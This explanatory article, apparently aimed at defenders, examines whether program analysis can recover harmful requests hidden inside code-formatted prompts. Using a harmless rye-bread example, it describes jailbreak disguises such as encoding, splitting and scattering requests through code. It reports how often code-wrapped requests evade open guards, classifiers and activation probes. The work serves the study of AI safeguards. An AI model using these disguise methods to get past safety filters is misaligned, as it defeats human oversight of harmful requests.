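# Can information flow analysis detect harmful intent hidden inside code-formatted prompts?

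## How a request can be hidden in code, and what information flow analysis tracks

A code-formatted prompt is a message to a language model in which program code carries some or all of the request. Most are ordinary, such as a programmer pasting in a function and asking where the bug is. But people also use code to get a request past a safety filter that would block it in plain English. The code stores the words in pieces or in an encoded form, and the model reassembles or decodes them. The hidden request is the plain-language request that the code stores, encodes or assembles.

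Since the 1970s, computer scientists have worked on methods for following data through programs, called information flow analysis. A tool could apply these methods to a prompt before the model sees it. This would help only if the tool could recover the hidden text in time and that text were enough to tell a harmful request from a harmless one.

### What a guard does

The filter is usually a guard, a learned classifier that screens what goes into or comes out of a language model. *Exploring and Developing a Pre-Model Safeguard with Draft Models* (2026) distinguishes guards that run before the main model from those that run after it. A pre-model guard checks only the prompt and can reject it before the main model runs. A post-model guard checks the prompt and response together, and the added context sometimes lets the same classifier catch a prompt it had passed as safe when checking the prompt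 alone. An exchange classifier also evaluates the model's output together with its input. Anthropic, which develops the Claude models, adopted one in *Constitutional Classifiers++* (2026) to replace two classifiers that had checked inputs and outputs separately.

*HaloGuard 1.0* (2026), an openly released guard, returns a safe-or-unsafe verdict, the policy category the prompt falls under, and a confidence score. An operator can use these to block clear cases automatically and send doubtful ones to a human reviewer. According to *A Reproducible, License-Aware Distillation Recipe for CPU-Deployable Safety Classification* (2026), current guards have between 1 and 9 billion parameters and need a graphics processor to answer at a usable speed.

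Code can hide a request because a guard responds to the surface form of a text. A request that the guard would block in plain words can get through as code, a cipher or formal logic, which Zhang, Wang and colleagues (2026) call the decode gap in *Blind, Not Weak*. Hong, Wu and colleagues (2025) sort the disguises into broad classes in *SoK*, a survey of 272 studies of prompt security. Two of these classes matter most for code. The first, obfuscation and encoding, changes how the text looks, and includes recasting it as code or markup. The second, decomposition, splits the request into innocent-looking parts for the model to recombine. Anthropic's *Next generation constitutional classifiers* describes a case that combines the two by scattering a harmful question through the functions of a codebase and instructing the model to extract it and respond.

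### Why a model can act on code that nobody runs

In a plain chat, the model has to work out what the program would produce from its text alone, because no interpreter runs the code.

Current models are good at predicting what a program will output when the run is short. *Evaluating Exact Output and Checkpoint-State Prediction in Real Programs* (2026) tested seven model settings on 400 cases drawn from contest solutions, textbook algorithms and a library routine, with tools and code execution switched off. The best setting predicted the exact final output in 93.0% of cases when the input led to a shorter run, and in 77.0% when the same program got an input that made it run longer. It correctly predicted the values of variables partway through a loop in 65.5% of cases. Accuracy depended heavily on step-by-step reasoning, with the same model scoring 74.8% overall at high reasoning and 25.2%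 at minimum reasoning.

Training can also improve the skill directly. In *Self-Execution Simulation Improves Coding Models*, Maimon, Yoran and colleagues (2026) recorded real program runs, had another model retell each run in ordinary words, and trained small models on the retellings. A 3-billion-parameter model improved from 37.5% to 68.0% on a standard test of predicting what short Python functions return.

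Joining a few words together is much easier than simulating a contest program, so it is unsurprising that simple disguises work. But Hong and colleagues found that an attack sometimes has a low success rate only because the model failed to carry out the transformed task, so a low rate doesn't show that the model is safe. An attacker can't make the task harder than the target model can handle, which also puts some limit on how hard a problem an analysis tool has to solve.

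### Taint tracking in four lines

Information flow analysis is the study of which values in a program can influence which other values. In the definition of Denning and Denning (1977), in *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow*, information flows from x to y whenever something stored in x moves to y, or helps to derive what moves to y. Taint tracking is the most widely used practical form. It marks ("taints") data from chosen sources and reports when marked data reaches chosen sinks, the places where its arrival matters. Four lines of Python are enough to show it:

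```python
x = get_input()
y = 1
w = x + y
send(w)
```

Line 1 is the source, so the tracker marks x. On line 2, y gets a constant and stays unmarked. Line 3 needs a propagation rule, and the usual one marks a result if any of its operands is marked. If t₁ and t₂ are the taint bits of the two operands, the result's bit is t₁ ∨ t₂, so w is marked. Line 4 is the sink, and the tracker reports that marked data has reached it. *All You Ever Wanted to Know About Dynamic Taint Analysis* (Schwartz, Avgerinos and Brumley, 2010) uses the term "taint policy" for the rules for how marks enter a program, how they spread and where the tracker checks for them. In a typical security setting, the source is a form on a web page and the sink is a database query.

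A tracker can work statically, by analysing the code without running it, or dynamically, by monitoring the code while it runs. A static tracker has to cover every path through the program, including some the program could never take, while a dynamic tracker covers only the path the program took.

The flow in the example is explicit: influence passes by assignment. Influence can also pass through which branch of the program is or is not taken, and that is an implicit flow. Denning and Denning's illustration, put into Python, assumes that x is either 0 or 1:

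```python
y = 1
if x == 0:
    y = 0
```

At the end y equals x, although no line copies x into y. Even if x is 1 and the assignment inside the branch doesn't run, you can still tell x from y. Most practical static tools don't track such flows, according to *Practical Type-Based Taint Checking and Inference* (Karimipour, Das and colleagues, 2025), which itself tracks only direct, or explicit, flows. *Taint Analysis via Heap-Aware Propagation* (2026) also treats explicit flows as the standard scope for its kind of analysis.

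That choice risks undertainting, which means missing a real flow. Overtainting is the opposite error, marking a value that does not depend on the source. Schwartz and colleagues give the example of a program that takes the exclusive-or of a value with itself. The result is always zero, but the simple propagation rule marks it anyway. Marks also tend to accumulate as a program runs, because the basic rules only add them. Reducing one error usually increases the other.

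Deobfuscation, one of two related techniques often discussed alongside taint tracking, rewrites disguised code or text into an equivalent form that is easy to read. Some tools work like an optimising compiler, calculating in advance any expression whose parts are all known and deleting code that can have no effect. Others hook into the interpreter and record what a script has unpacked by the time it runs. Newer ones use a language model for some or all of the rewriting.

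Symbolic execution runs a program on unknowns instead of concrete values and records the conditions under which it takes each path. Another example program from Schwartz and colleagues reads a number, doubles it, adds one, and fails if the result minus five equals fourteen. Ordinary testing could try many numbers before triggering the failure. A symbolic executor represents the input as s and the computed result as 2s + 1. At the branch, it records the condition 2s + 1 − 5 = 14 for the failing path and its negation for the other. A solver then finds that s = 9 causes the failure. But every branch that depends on an unknown can split the analysis in two, and a loop can keep splitting it without end.

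### A request for rye bread

A harmless prompt will serve as the running example. It has a snippet of Python:

```python
words = ["How", "do", "I", "bake", "rye", "bread"]
task = " ".join(words)
```

and one English sentence after it, asking the model to answer the question in `task`. The full question never appears as one string in the prompt. A capable model will give a recipe all the same.

The difficulty of recovering the question depends on how the code stores it. *SCRIPTIOC-BENCH* (Kim, Cui and colleagues, 2026) presents a benchmark of malicious scripts and a three-level scale of difficulty that also fits prompts well. At the direct level, the string appears verbatim, as in `task = "How do I bake rye bread"`, and a text search finds it. At the fixed-transform level, a standard decoder can recover the string through routine operations, such as decoding Base64 or joining a list of literals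 like the one in the snippet above. At the program-dependent level, a person or tool has to follow the program's own logic. The rye bread question would be at this level if the list held the words out of order and a function written for this one snippet put them in order.

Kim and colleagues assign a level to each string, so one script can contain strings at all three levels. Calling a string program-dependent means only that the fixed decoder failed on it. Their benchmark includes only statically recoverable strings, meaning that the script and the data inside it fully determine their values. Strings in malware may not be recoverable this way, because malware can fetch missing data from a server at run time. A model without tools can't fetch anything, so whatever it uses to rebuild a hidden request must already be in the conversation or in what the model learned in training, which is an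 advantage for the analyst.

### Sources and sinks in a prompt

To use taint tracking on the rye bread prompt, someone has to specify the sources and the sink. Denning and Denning put constants in the lowest security class, reasoning that writing "99" into a variable reveals nothing about any other object. Schwartz and colleagues' typical policy leaves constants unmarked too. A tracker with those defaults would mark nothing in the rye bread snippet, because the snippet reads no input. The request is in the literals, so a tracker for prompts has to treat them as sources.

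Names and comments need the same treatment. *When Names Disappear* (2025) describes code as having two channels of meaning, the formal behaviour of the program and the human-readable names in it. An interpreter needs only the first, but models use both. In *CodeCrash*, Lam, Huang and colleagues (2025) changed the text around the logic of programs without changing their results, then tested how well 17 models predicted the outputs. False comments lowered accuracy by 13.5 percentage points, and false messages in print statements lowered it by 13.3. Replacing meaningful names with placeholders reduced accuracy by 8.2 points on one set of problems, but by only 2.4 on a second set, where the functions had no meaningful names to begin with. In *On the Lexical Superstition of Large Language Models for Code Comprehension*, Shen, Xi and colleagues (2026) replaced a program's names with names from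 an unrelated program, and the models' answers often drifted towards what the borrowed names suggested.

Both groups tested models from 2025 or earlier, and newer ones may be harder to mislead. But the argument here requires only that names and comments reach the model. A variable called `rye_bread_recipe` gives a model information even if the program never uses the variable. Many program analysis tools lose this information at the first step. Parsing code into a syntax tree typically removes the comments, which is how Lam and colleagues prepared their clean versions, and some deobfuscators rename the variables.

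The sink is harder to identify. It is the place where text becomes the model's instruction, which in the example is `task`. Only the English sentence makes `task` a sink, so if that sentence were changed to "How many words are in the list?", the sink would disappear even though the code stayed the same. Taint trackers expect a person to supply the list of sinks, and Karimipour and colleagues describe finding the right rules as a research problem in itself, even for ordinary software. For a prompt, a language model or a human would have to read the English to work out the rule. A crude alternative is to treat every variable as a sink, but the tracker then reports nearly every string in nearly every innocent programming question.

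The other difficulty is that a model interprets the code, whereas program analysis assumes a language with fixed rules. Schwartz and colleagues build both taint analysis and symbolic execution on a language's operational semantics, the exact rules for what each statement does. Code in a prompt doesn't have to follow those rules. It may contain a syntax error or call a function that nobody defined. Python would stop there, but a model will often continue and guess from the function's name what it was supposed to do. Models also make mistakes on code that runs correctly, and even the best setting in the output-prediction benchmark got 7% of the shorter runs wrong. So a program analysis tool can establish what Python would compute, but a filter has to predict how the model will interpret the code. The two will almost always agree for something like the rye bread snippet, but an attacker has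 good reason to look for code where they differ.

### Recovering the text and judging it

Even if the tool handles all of this and recovers the request "How do I bake rye bread", taint tracking cannot judge whether that request is harmful.

In a database attack, the flow itself is the fault because untrusted text should never become part of a command. In a prompt, however, the user's words are supposed to reach the model's instruction, so the flow alone is not evidence of harmful intent. The analysis would report that six literals flow into `task` whether they spelled out a harmless request or a request for a weapon. A second component, in practice a guard, has to read the recovered sentence and judge whether it is harmful, and it can make the same errors there as on plain text.

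Zhang and colleagues built a pipeline of this kind. The target model first restates an encoded request in plain language, and a guard classifies the restatement. If the restatement passes, the target answers the original message. When the request was wrapped in code, the restatement could lose the signal the guard depended on, even if the recovery looked successful. Program analysis might do better on this point because it would return the literal strings instead of a paraphrase.

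Running the rye bread snippet only builds a string in memory. Running it would still be harmless if the string held a dangerous question, because the harm lies in what the message asks and would come with the model's answer. By contrast, a script that reads a file of passwords and sends it to an outside server is harmful because of what the code does, even though every string in it may look innocuous. Information flow analysis was made for this second problem, where the forbidden flow is itself the violation. Denning and Denning wanted to prove that a program could not let confidential inputs affect supposedly non-confidential results.

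Much of the available evidence comes from the second kind of case, malware and malicious agent skills. Agent skills are packages of instructions and scripts that an AI agent loads to do a job. A high detection rate on such material is little evidence of how well a detector finds hidden questions, since it can reach that rate by spotting suspicious behaviour that a code-formatted prompt never shows. Kim and colleagues' benchmark is more relevant than most because, although its scripts are malware, the task is to recover strings such as web addresses from them.

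## How learned classifiers do on requests wrapped in code

Many operators already run a guard in front of their model, so program analysis is worth adding only where guards fail. On requests wrapped in code, the failure rate depends heavily on how much information the guard has. In a matched comparison of plain text and code, five open guards that check only the prompt missed more than half of the wrapped requests. A system that Anthropic described in January 2026, which also monitors the model's answer and internal activity, let through one serious attack in about 198,000 attempts.

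### From text to a verdict

Most guards start as ordinary language models. Developers collect prompts and answers, label each one safe or unsafe under a written policy, and train the model further until it produces the right label. Anthropic generates synthetic examples from a "constitution", a set of plain-language rules about what the model may and may not help with. These rules allow help with college chemistry homework, for instance, but not with making Schedule 1 chemicals. The first classifiers trained this way cut the success rate of jailbreaks (prompts designed to get around a model's safeguards) from 86% to 4.4%, but increased computing costs by 23.7%.

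Training rewards only the correct label, whatever the source of the examples. A guard can therefore score well without working out what a program would compute, as long as few of its training examples require this.

The output of such a guard is a probability for each possible next word. To get a score, Zhang and colleagues took the probabilities of the two verdict words and rescaled them to add up to one:

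score = P(unsafe) / (P(safe) + P(unsafe))

Suppose a guard assigns the rye bread prompt a probability of 0.92 for "safe" and 0.02 for "unsafe". The score is 0.02 / (0.92 + 0.02), or about 0.02. The operator chooses a threshold and blocks every prompt that scores above it. A guard that prints the more likely verdict has a threshold of 0.5.

Lowering the threshold raises both recall, the share of harmful requests that the guard catches, and the false positive rate, the share of harmless requests that it blocks. *Constitutional Classifiers++* fixed the false positive rate first, setting each classifier's threshold so that it refused 0.1% of the conversations in WildChat, a public collection of real chatbot use, and then measured how many attacks got past. But moving a threshold only helps if harmful prompts score higher than harmless ones. If a code wrapper lowers a harmful request's score into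 the range of ordinary programming questions, no threshold will separate them.

### The same requests, plain and in code

To test whether code has this effect, Zhang and colleagues gave five open guards the same harmful requests in plain English and again inside a code template from a published attack. The requests came from HarmBench, a standard test set, and the guards were WildGuard, Llama Guard 3, Qwen3Guard, ThinkGuard and GuardReasoner-VL. A blocked prompt always triggers the same refusal message, so the researchers could count blocks without a second model to interpret the results.

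The five guards blocked 97.4% of the plain requests and 43.4% of the same requests in code. For four of them, the drop was too large and one-sided to be plausibly due to chance (p ≤ 1.3 × 10⁻¹²). The fifth, Llama Guard 3, blocked 94% in both forms. If 43.4% is a simple average over the five guards, the other four blocked about 31% of the code versions.

Llama Guard 3 blocked about 94% of harmful requests in both plain and code form, but its block rate on harmless requests rose from 10% in plain form to 61% in code. The gap between its block rates on harmful and harmless requests therefore shrank from 84 points to 33. None of the other guards blocked harmless requests more often when they were in code. Llama Guard 3 may have been trained on similar attacks and learned to treat the code wrapper itself as a warning sign, but the test can't show whether this happened.

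Either way, the verdicts changed while the meaning stayed the same, which is good evidence that these guards respond to form. They may have learned to recognise sentences that ask for something harmful, which the code breaks up. This is more likely than simple keyword matching, because the template leaves the words of the request readable in the prompt, so a crude keyword filter might have done better than some of these guards.

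On this test, a program analysis tool that recovered every request exactly could raise the average block rate from 43.4% to at most 97.4%. With Llama Guard 3, it would not improve recall, but it might reduce the false positive rate from 61% towards 10%.

The plain-text figure makes these guards look better than they are, though, because some of them are very strict. OR-Bench-Hard is a set of harmless requests that resemble harmful ones. With WildGuard in place, the system refused 79% of those it received as text, although the model behind the guard made some of those refusals. A guard that judged recovered text would be just as strict.

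With no guard, the small open model Qwen2.5-VL-7B gave harmful answers to 59 of 100 code-wrapped requests. Llama Guard 3 cut that number to 2, ThinkGuard to 25, Qwen3Guard to 41 and WildGuard to 45. With GuardReasoner-VL the number was 61, so that guard gave no protection, even though it writes out its reasoning before giving a verdict.

WildGuard blocked a smaller share of requests in classical Chinese and Base64 than in code. It blocked 54% of requests rewritten as set theory, 29% in formal logic, 28% in code, 20% in classical Chinese and none in Base64, a standard way of writing data as letters, digits and a few symbols. The Base64 misses had almost no effect because Qwen2.5-VL-7B can't read Base64, but WildGuard would not protect a more capable model from these requests. Base64 is also the easiest of these formats for a conventional tool to decode. Zhang and colleagues ran 120 of their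 encoded requests through a decoder, which recovered every one exactly.

Changing the threshold would have helped only one of the five guards, Llama Guard 3. The researchers tested each guard across its full range of thresholds against an attacker who could choose among eleven disguises. They allowed the system to refuse at most 35% of the harmless OR-Bench-Hard requests. Without a guard, the model already refused about 26%. For the other four guards, the only threshold within the limit blocked nothing.

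These results come from one code template and five open guards. Another template could give quite different numbers, especially for Llama Guard 3 if that model has learned to recognise this one.

### Two broader benchmarks

Larger comparisons cover more guards but are less informative about code. In *TRACE*, Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026) tested 18 guards on 1,993 prompts in English and Chinese, 57% of them unsafe. The unsafe prompts came from a collection with ten kinds of attack, including code injection and encryption of the request. The guards averaged an F1 score of 75.75% on prompts. F1 combines recall with precision, the share of blocked items that were harmful. The best guard, PolyGuard-8B, scored 91.17%, missing 9.58% of unsafe prompts and blocking 9.11% of safe ones.

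This broader mix of requests also includes results for three of the guards from the plain-versus-code test. Qwen3Guard-8B scored 88.43% and WildGuard 86.37%. Llama Guard 3, the one that kept blocking when requests were in code, scored lowest of the three at 73.14%. Its larger successor, Llama Guard 4, scored even lower, at 66.52%.

Encrypting the request with Base64 or a simple letter-shifting cipher reduced the guards' performance more than any of the other nine attacks, whether the guards were judging the prompt, the model's written reasoning or its final answer. PolyGuard-8B's F1 was 29.89% on final answers to encrypted prompts, compared with 84.15% on all final answers. For YuFeng-XGuard-8B, the strongest guard on answers overall, F1 was 35.16%, compared with 86.11%.

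Those drops may exaggerate the problem. The answers came from small models, which probably failed to decode many of the prompts and so produced few harmful answers. When harmful cases are rare, even a modest number of false alarms lowers F1 sharply.

Wu and colleagues also tested whether guards could identify the words that justified a verdict. Only four of the 18 guards give explanations, and the highest overlap between those explanations and the evidence that annotators had marked in the prompts was 11.68%. Some of the mismatch may come from guards that explain at length where the annotators quoted a phrase. Still, today's guards offer little help to an operator who wants to know which part of a long code file caused a block, whereas a taint tracker routinely reports the location.

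An older benchmark, *POLY-GUARD* (Kang, Chen and colleagues, 2025), which is separate from the PolyGuard model above, compared 19 guards across eight domains, one of them code generation. NVIDIA's Aegis Defensive had the highest recall in that domain, at 56.1%. GPT-4o, a general-purpose model set up as a guard, reached 33.1%. These figures do not measure how well guards detect requests hidden inside code, because the prompts ask for unsafe code itself, such as programs with insecure patterns.

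Llama Guard 3 caught only 7.5% of the requests in this domain, although it blocked 94% of the code-wrapped requests in the matched test. The low rate may be because its policy doesn't cover insecure code, but the contrast still makes it harder to attribute the 94% to an understanding of programs.

Kang and colleagues also found that guards did better on conversations than on single requests, which suggests that extra context helps.

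### Checking the answer as well

An exchange classifier gets that extra context from the model's answer. *Constitutional Classifiers++* switched to one after testers got scattered requests past the previous system's input classifier. The new classifier first scores the prompt alone, then scores the exchange in batches of tokens as the model writes. To answer a scattered request, the model often has to put the pieces back together, and the result tends to resemble the ciphers that the input classifiers had already learned to block. The paper reused the input classifier for the new role without special training.

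They then had human testers attack both designs. The testers looked for a single strategy that would get detailed answers to eight questions about chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. An attack counted as a high-risk vulnerability if, on more than five of the eight questions, it got answers at least half as detailed as an unguarded model would give.

Testers found 13 such vulnerabilities in 695,000 queries to the older design, which had separate input and output classifiers. They found 2 in 226,000 queries to the exchange classifier, about half the rate. Four of the attacks on the older design worked on all eight questions and took an average of 27 hours to find. Only one attack on the exchange classifier worked on all eight, and it took 100 hours to find.

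Two cases are very little evidence. If both designs were equally weak, a split at least this favourable to the exchange classifier would occur by chance about one time in four. The designs also protected different models, Claude Sonnet 3.7 and Claude Opus 4, though the team doubts that this mattered much. The evidence for exchange classification is stronger when the two later systems are included, because the three designs that use it had a total of 8 vulnerabilities in 993,000 queries.

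Judging a chat model's answer as it appears is usually early enough, because the operator can cut it off partway. This weakens the case for recovering the request beforehand. However, the model still uses compute to generate the start of an answer that nobody should get, and the exchange classifier needed about 50% more compute than the pair it replaced.

Hiding a request also gets the attacker less accurate answers. The team tested Claude Opus 4 on GPQA Diamond, a set of very hard multiple-choice science questions, using two attacks that split up the question and disguise the answer. Accuracy fell from 74.2% to 32.3% with one attack and to 49% with the other. The first result is little better than the 25% expected from guessing among four options.

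An attacker who wants reliable instructions for something difficult has good reason to avoid a disguise like that. But the second attack kept far more of the model's ability, and the team expects attackers to find others that reduce it less. The figures also include the ability lost by disguising the answer, a step that an attacker facing only a prompt filter could skip. Claude Opus 4 dates from 2025, so newer models may lose less.

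### A cascade and a probe

Running a large classifier on every exchange is wasteful when nearly all traffic is harmless. The next system in *Constitutional Classifiers++* therefore used two classifiers in sequence. A small one checked everything and passed about 10% of traffic to one roughly three times its size. The small classifier could raise many false alarms because a flag led to a second check, not a refusal. Together with more efficient models and software, this cut compute to less than a fifth of what the exchange classifier used. Testers found vulnerabilities at almost the same rate as before. Experts outside the bounty programme found universal attacks, though this took substantial effort and automated tools.

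Even then, the small classifier made up about 77% of the bill. The final system replaced it with a linear probe, a very simple classifier that works on the model's own activations, the numbers that the model computes internally as it processes each token. At token t, the probe's estimate that the exchange is harmful is

p(harmful | x₁ … xₜ) = σ(W·ψₜ + b)

Here x₁ … xₜ is the text so far, and ψₜ is a list of activations at token t from every layer of the model. Training sets the weights W and the constant b. The probe multiplies each activation by its weight, sums the results, adds b, and uses the function σ to convert the total into a probability.

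Running a probe on the model's activations adds almost no computation because the model has already produced them. For a 27-billion-parameter model, the team put the probe's computation at about 377,000 arithmetic operations per token, compared with about 8 billion for a separate classifier with 4 billion parameters.

The plain formula had two weaknesses in training. One was that a single odd token could set off an alarm, so the team averaged the total W·ψₜ + b over 16 consecutive tokens. The other came from the labels, which applied to whole exchanges. A harmful exchange may open with a long stretch of innocent text, and ordinary training would teach the probe to be suspicious of the opening too. The team therefore weighted each token's contribution to the training error by

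wₜ = exp(z̄ₜ) / Σₛ exp(z̄ₛ)

where z̄ₜ is the averaged total at token t and the sum runs over all scored positions in the exchange. A token with an average of +3 gets about 400 times the weight of one at −3. The probe can then treat the opening as harmless at almost no penalty, and training concentrates on the places where it is most confident of harm. That should suit code-formatted prompts, which can look like ordinary programming until the pieces come together.

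On about 7,000 exchanges from earlier red-teaming, the best probe missed roughly 1.4% of attacks. It beat the small classifier from the cascade and nearly matched the larger one, although it flagged more harmless scientific questions. Combining the probe with the larger classifier worked better than using either alone. Their scores were less correlated than those of the two ordinary classifiers, so each could catch some attacks the other missed. The researchers chose the mixing weights on the same data they used to measure the result, so the gain looks somewhat larger than it would on new attacks.

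In the final system, the probe checks every exchange and sends about 5.5% of traffic to the larger classifier. The decision then rests on a weighted sum of the two scores, 0.55 for the probe and 0.45 for the classifier. The four systems compare as follows, with computing cost relative to the oldest:

| System | High-risk vulnerabilities | Red-team queries | Relative computing cost | Production traffic refused |
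|---|---|---|---|---|
| Separate input and output classifiers | 13 | 695,000 | 100 | 0.073% |
| Exchange classifier | 2 | 226,000 | 150 | 0.038% |
| Two-classifier cascade | 5 | 569,000 | 27.8 | 0.036% |
| Probe, then probe and classifier | 1 | 198,000 | 3.5 | 0.050% |

The final system uses about one-fortieth of the computation that the exchange classifier does. Anthropic estimates that it adds roughly 1% to computation on Claude Opus 4 traffic. During a month-long trial on live Claude Sonnet 4.5 traffic, it flagged 0.05% of queries. In more than 1,700 hours of red-teaming, nobody found an attack that worked on all eight questions.

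These numbers are hard to compare with those for the open guards. Anthropic's classifiers cover a narrow group of weapons topics that seldom come up in ordinary traffic, so a low refusal rate is easier to achieve. The open guards cover many kinds of harm, and Zhang and colleagues measured their false positives on requests chosen to look harmful. The probe system's performance on the full range of HarmBench requests in code is unknown.

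### What a probe can pick up from code

A probe is attractive for requests hidden in code because it can use the model's own decoding of them. A separate guard has to decode the request itself, and may be worse at that than the model it protects. If the model has decoded a snippet as "How do I bake rye bread", its activations should contain some trace of bread, however the code stored the words. Anthropic makes the related claim that attackers will find it much harder to manipulate a model's internal representations than its output.

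The red-teaming results are consistent with this idea but don't test it on its own. Testers attacked the probe and the classifier together, so their failure doesn't show how much of the resistance came from the probe. The main results also combine all kinds of jailbreak and give no separate catch rate for requests in code. A flag at any point in the exchange counts as a success, so the probe may often have responded to harmful material in the answer. That would still protect the user, but it wouldn't show that the model represented the hidden request as harmful while processing the prompt.

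A probe that reads activations at the end of the prompt may not always detect harmful intent wrapped in code. When Zhang and colleagues asked Qwen2.5-VL-7B to restate code-wrapped requests in plain English, it got only 4% right, yet it gave harmful answers to 59% of them when told to respond. Evidently the model could act on a request that it couldn't state in advance. It may piece the request together only as it writes its answer, which would leave little for a probe to detect at the end of the prompt. However, a restatement is only indirect evidence about activations, and a much larger model may behave differently.

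A model can also decode a request without treating it as harmful. Two of the four models that produced answers for Wu and colleagues had undergone abliteration, an editing technique that suppresses a model's refusals but leaves most of its general ability intact. Such a model can understand a harmful request and still not refuse it. Its internal signs of harm may remain, since refusing and recognising harm may be separate. Even so, a model's ability to decode a request doesn't guarantee that a probe will detect the harm in it.

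The probe's training raises a similar concern. In the main experiments, another classifier labeled the probe's training data, so if a disguise fooled that classifier, the probe could have learned to treat the exchange as harmless. The team got similar results using labels taken directly from its synthetic data, which makes this less worrying, at least for the kinds of attack in that data.

A more direct test would compare the probe's scores on matched requests in plain text and in code, measured at the last token of the prompt, before the model has written anything. If the scores agreed, program analysis would add little wherever a probe is available. Only someone who runs the model can read the activations a probe needs, so a company that reaches a model through another firm's interface has just the text of the prompt and the answer.

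## Static analysis: recovering the text without running the code

An operator with only the text of a prompt can still analyse its code as an optimising compiler would, because a hidden request can usually be worked out from the source code alone. Nobody seems to have published a test of this analysis on harmful requests wrapped in code, so the measurements come from related problems, mainly deobfuscating malicious JavaScript.

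### From the prompt to a syntax tree

A slightly longer rye bread prompt can show each step. Part of the question is now in Base64, and some of the code has nothing to do with it:

```
1  import base64
2  title = "Kitchen timer"
3  start = ["How", "do", "I", "bake"]
4  end = base64.b64decode("cnllIGJyZWFk").decode()
5  minutes = 5 * 9
6  task = " ".join(start) + " " + end
7  print(title, minutes)
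```

One English sentence after the code asks the model to answer the question in `task`.

The tool first has to find the code. Many users put code between fence markers, which show where it starts and ends. Without them, the tool can try a parser on successive blocks of lines and keep the blocks that parse. English sentences rarely parse as Python, although a line with only the word "Thanks" does, because it could be a variable name.

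The parser turns the code into a syntax tree, which shows which operation applies to which operands. Line 6 becomes:

```
assign to task
  add
    add
      join
        " "
        start
      " "
    end
```

For ordinary programming languages, parsing time grows roughly in proportion to the length of the code.

Next the tool needs a sink. Assume for now that a small language model has read the English sentence and returned "`task`, line 6".

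### Slicing back from the sink

A backward slice is the set of statements that can influence a chosen variable at a chosen line. Mark Weiser introduced program slicing decades ago, and programmers use it mostly for debugging. According to *SLICEFORMER* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026), a correct slice contains every relevant statement and no others, copied exactly and in the original order.

Traditional slicers build a dependence graph. It links each statement to the statements that set the variables it uses, and to the branches that decide whether it runs. If D(s) is the set of statements that s depends on directly, the slice for statement n is the smallest set S such that

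n ∈ S, and D(s) ⊆ S for every s in S

Here D(6) = {3, 4} and D(4) = {1}, while line 3 depends on nothing. The slice is therefore lines 1, 3, 4 and 6:

```
1  import base64
3  start = ["How", "do", "I", "bake"]
4  end = base64.b64decode("cnllIGJyZWFk").decode()
6  task = " ".join(start) + " " + end
```

The slice leaves out the timer code. *Program Slicing in the Era of Large Language Models* (2024) points out that a static slice can be larger than necessary because it allows for every possible path through the code.

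Once the graph exists, the time to compute a slice is proportional to the number of links. In large programs, building the graph takes the most time and memory, because the tool has to work out which function each call reaches and which variables refer to the same data. Karimipour and colleagues cite an analysis that needed over three hours and 153 GB of memory, but it covered the full Java standard library, which is far larger than almost any prompt.

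### Propagating, folding and decoding

Constant propagation keeps a record of what the tool can say about each variable at each point in the program. Jiang, Kovuri and colleagues (2025), in *CASCADE*, describe the version in Google's own JavaScript deobfuscator. A variable is Uninit (no value yet), Const(c) (certainly the value c) or Unknown. The main rules are:

```
x = c             x becomes Const(c)

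x = y + z         x becomes Const(a + b) if y is Const(a) and z is Const(b)
                  x becomes Unknown if y or z is Unknown

two paths meet    Const(a) and Const(a) give Const(a)
                  Const(a) and Const(b) give Unknown, if a and b differ
                  Uninit and any value v give v
```

The rule for addition works for any operation the tool can calculate. This calculation, called constant folding, replaces an expression made only of constants with its result. Fixed decoders do the same for standard encodings such as Base64.

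The tool repeats these passes until nothing changes:

```
Round 1   propagate   task = " ".join(["How", "do", "I", "bake"]) + " " + end
          fold        task = "How do I bake " + end
          decode      end = "rye bread"
Round 2   propagate   task = "How do I bake " + "rye bread"
          fold        task = "How do I bake rye bread"
Round 3   no change
```

Propagation always finishes, because at each point in the program a variable can only move from Uninit to Const to Unknown. With n points and v variables, there are at most 2nv changes. Doubling both the program's length and its number of variables can therefore quadruple the work, which is still trivial for a snippet of a few hundred lines. Folding can take far more work, because forty lines that each double the length of a string would make it about a trillion times as long. The tool therefore needs a limit on string length.

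The decoders need limits too. If the code calls a standard decoder, the tool can safely do the same. But the English part of a prompt might contain an instruction to decode a string that the code never decodes, so the tool may also need to try its decoders on any string that looks encoded. This produces a lot of junk, since even an ordinary word like "bake" is valid Base64 and decodes to three meaningless bytes. The tool should keep a decoded version only if it is readable text, and should keep the original beside it.

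*AgentTrust* (Yang, 2026) checks AI agents' shell commands in a similar way. The software rewrites a command in up to nine ways, such as expanding variables and decoding escape codes, but never executes it. It then checks the original and all the rewritten versions, and uses the most severe verdict. It reached the right verdict on about 93% of disguised commands, with a typical delay of a few milliseconds. Yang had already patched the rules before this test and doesn't present the test as unseen, so new disguises may well evade the software more often.

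### What taint labels add

Constant folding alone would recover every string in the program, "Kitchen timer" included. Taint labels show which of them end up in the sink. Each literal gets its own label, and a result inherits the labels of everything that went into it:

labels(literal i) = {i}

labels(y + z) = labels(y) ∪ labels(z)

At the end, `task` carries the labels of the four words on line 3, the Base64 string on line 4 and the two spaces on line 6. In this example the slice had already removed the timer's title. But a slice keeps or drops whole statements, so if one list held both the title and the words of the question, the slice would keep the entire list. With a separate label for each element, the title could still be distinguished from the question.

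Each extra string a guard checks is another chance of a false alarm. Suppose a guard wrongly flags one harmless string in a thousand, and a pasted file contains 200 strings. If the errors are independent, the guard will flag at least one string in 18% of such files. If the labels narrow the 200 strings to five, the figure drops to 0.5%. This most helps people whose files have good reason to contain a lot of alarming text, such as a moderator's list of banned phrases.

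However, ignoring the other strings is safe only if the tool has the right sink. The model reads the whole prompt, including the parts that the slice leaves out. Cheng, Yu and colleagues (2026), in *CodeSentinel*, treat disconnected code in the opposite way, as a warning sign. Their tool protects coding assistants from instructions that a third party has planted in code. It scores a piece of code as

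risk = salience × (1 − reachability)

Salience estimates how much a piece of the program will attract the model's attention, and reachability measures how well that piece connects to the program's main logic. A striking string that the program never uses gets a high score. A prompt filter could reasonably judge both whatever reaches the sink and whatever stands out but reaches nothing.

### Handing the text to a guard

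The last step is to give the recovered string, "How do I bake rye bread", to a guard. Ideally the tool would first put the string back into the prompt's English sentence, because an attacker can leave part of the request there. A string that contains only "rye bread" could belong to many questions.

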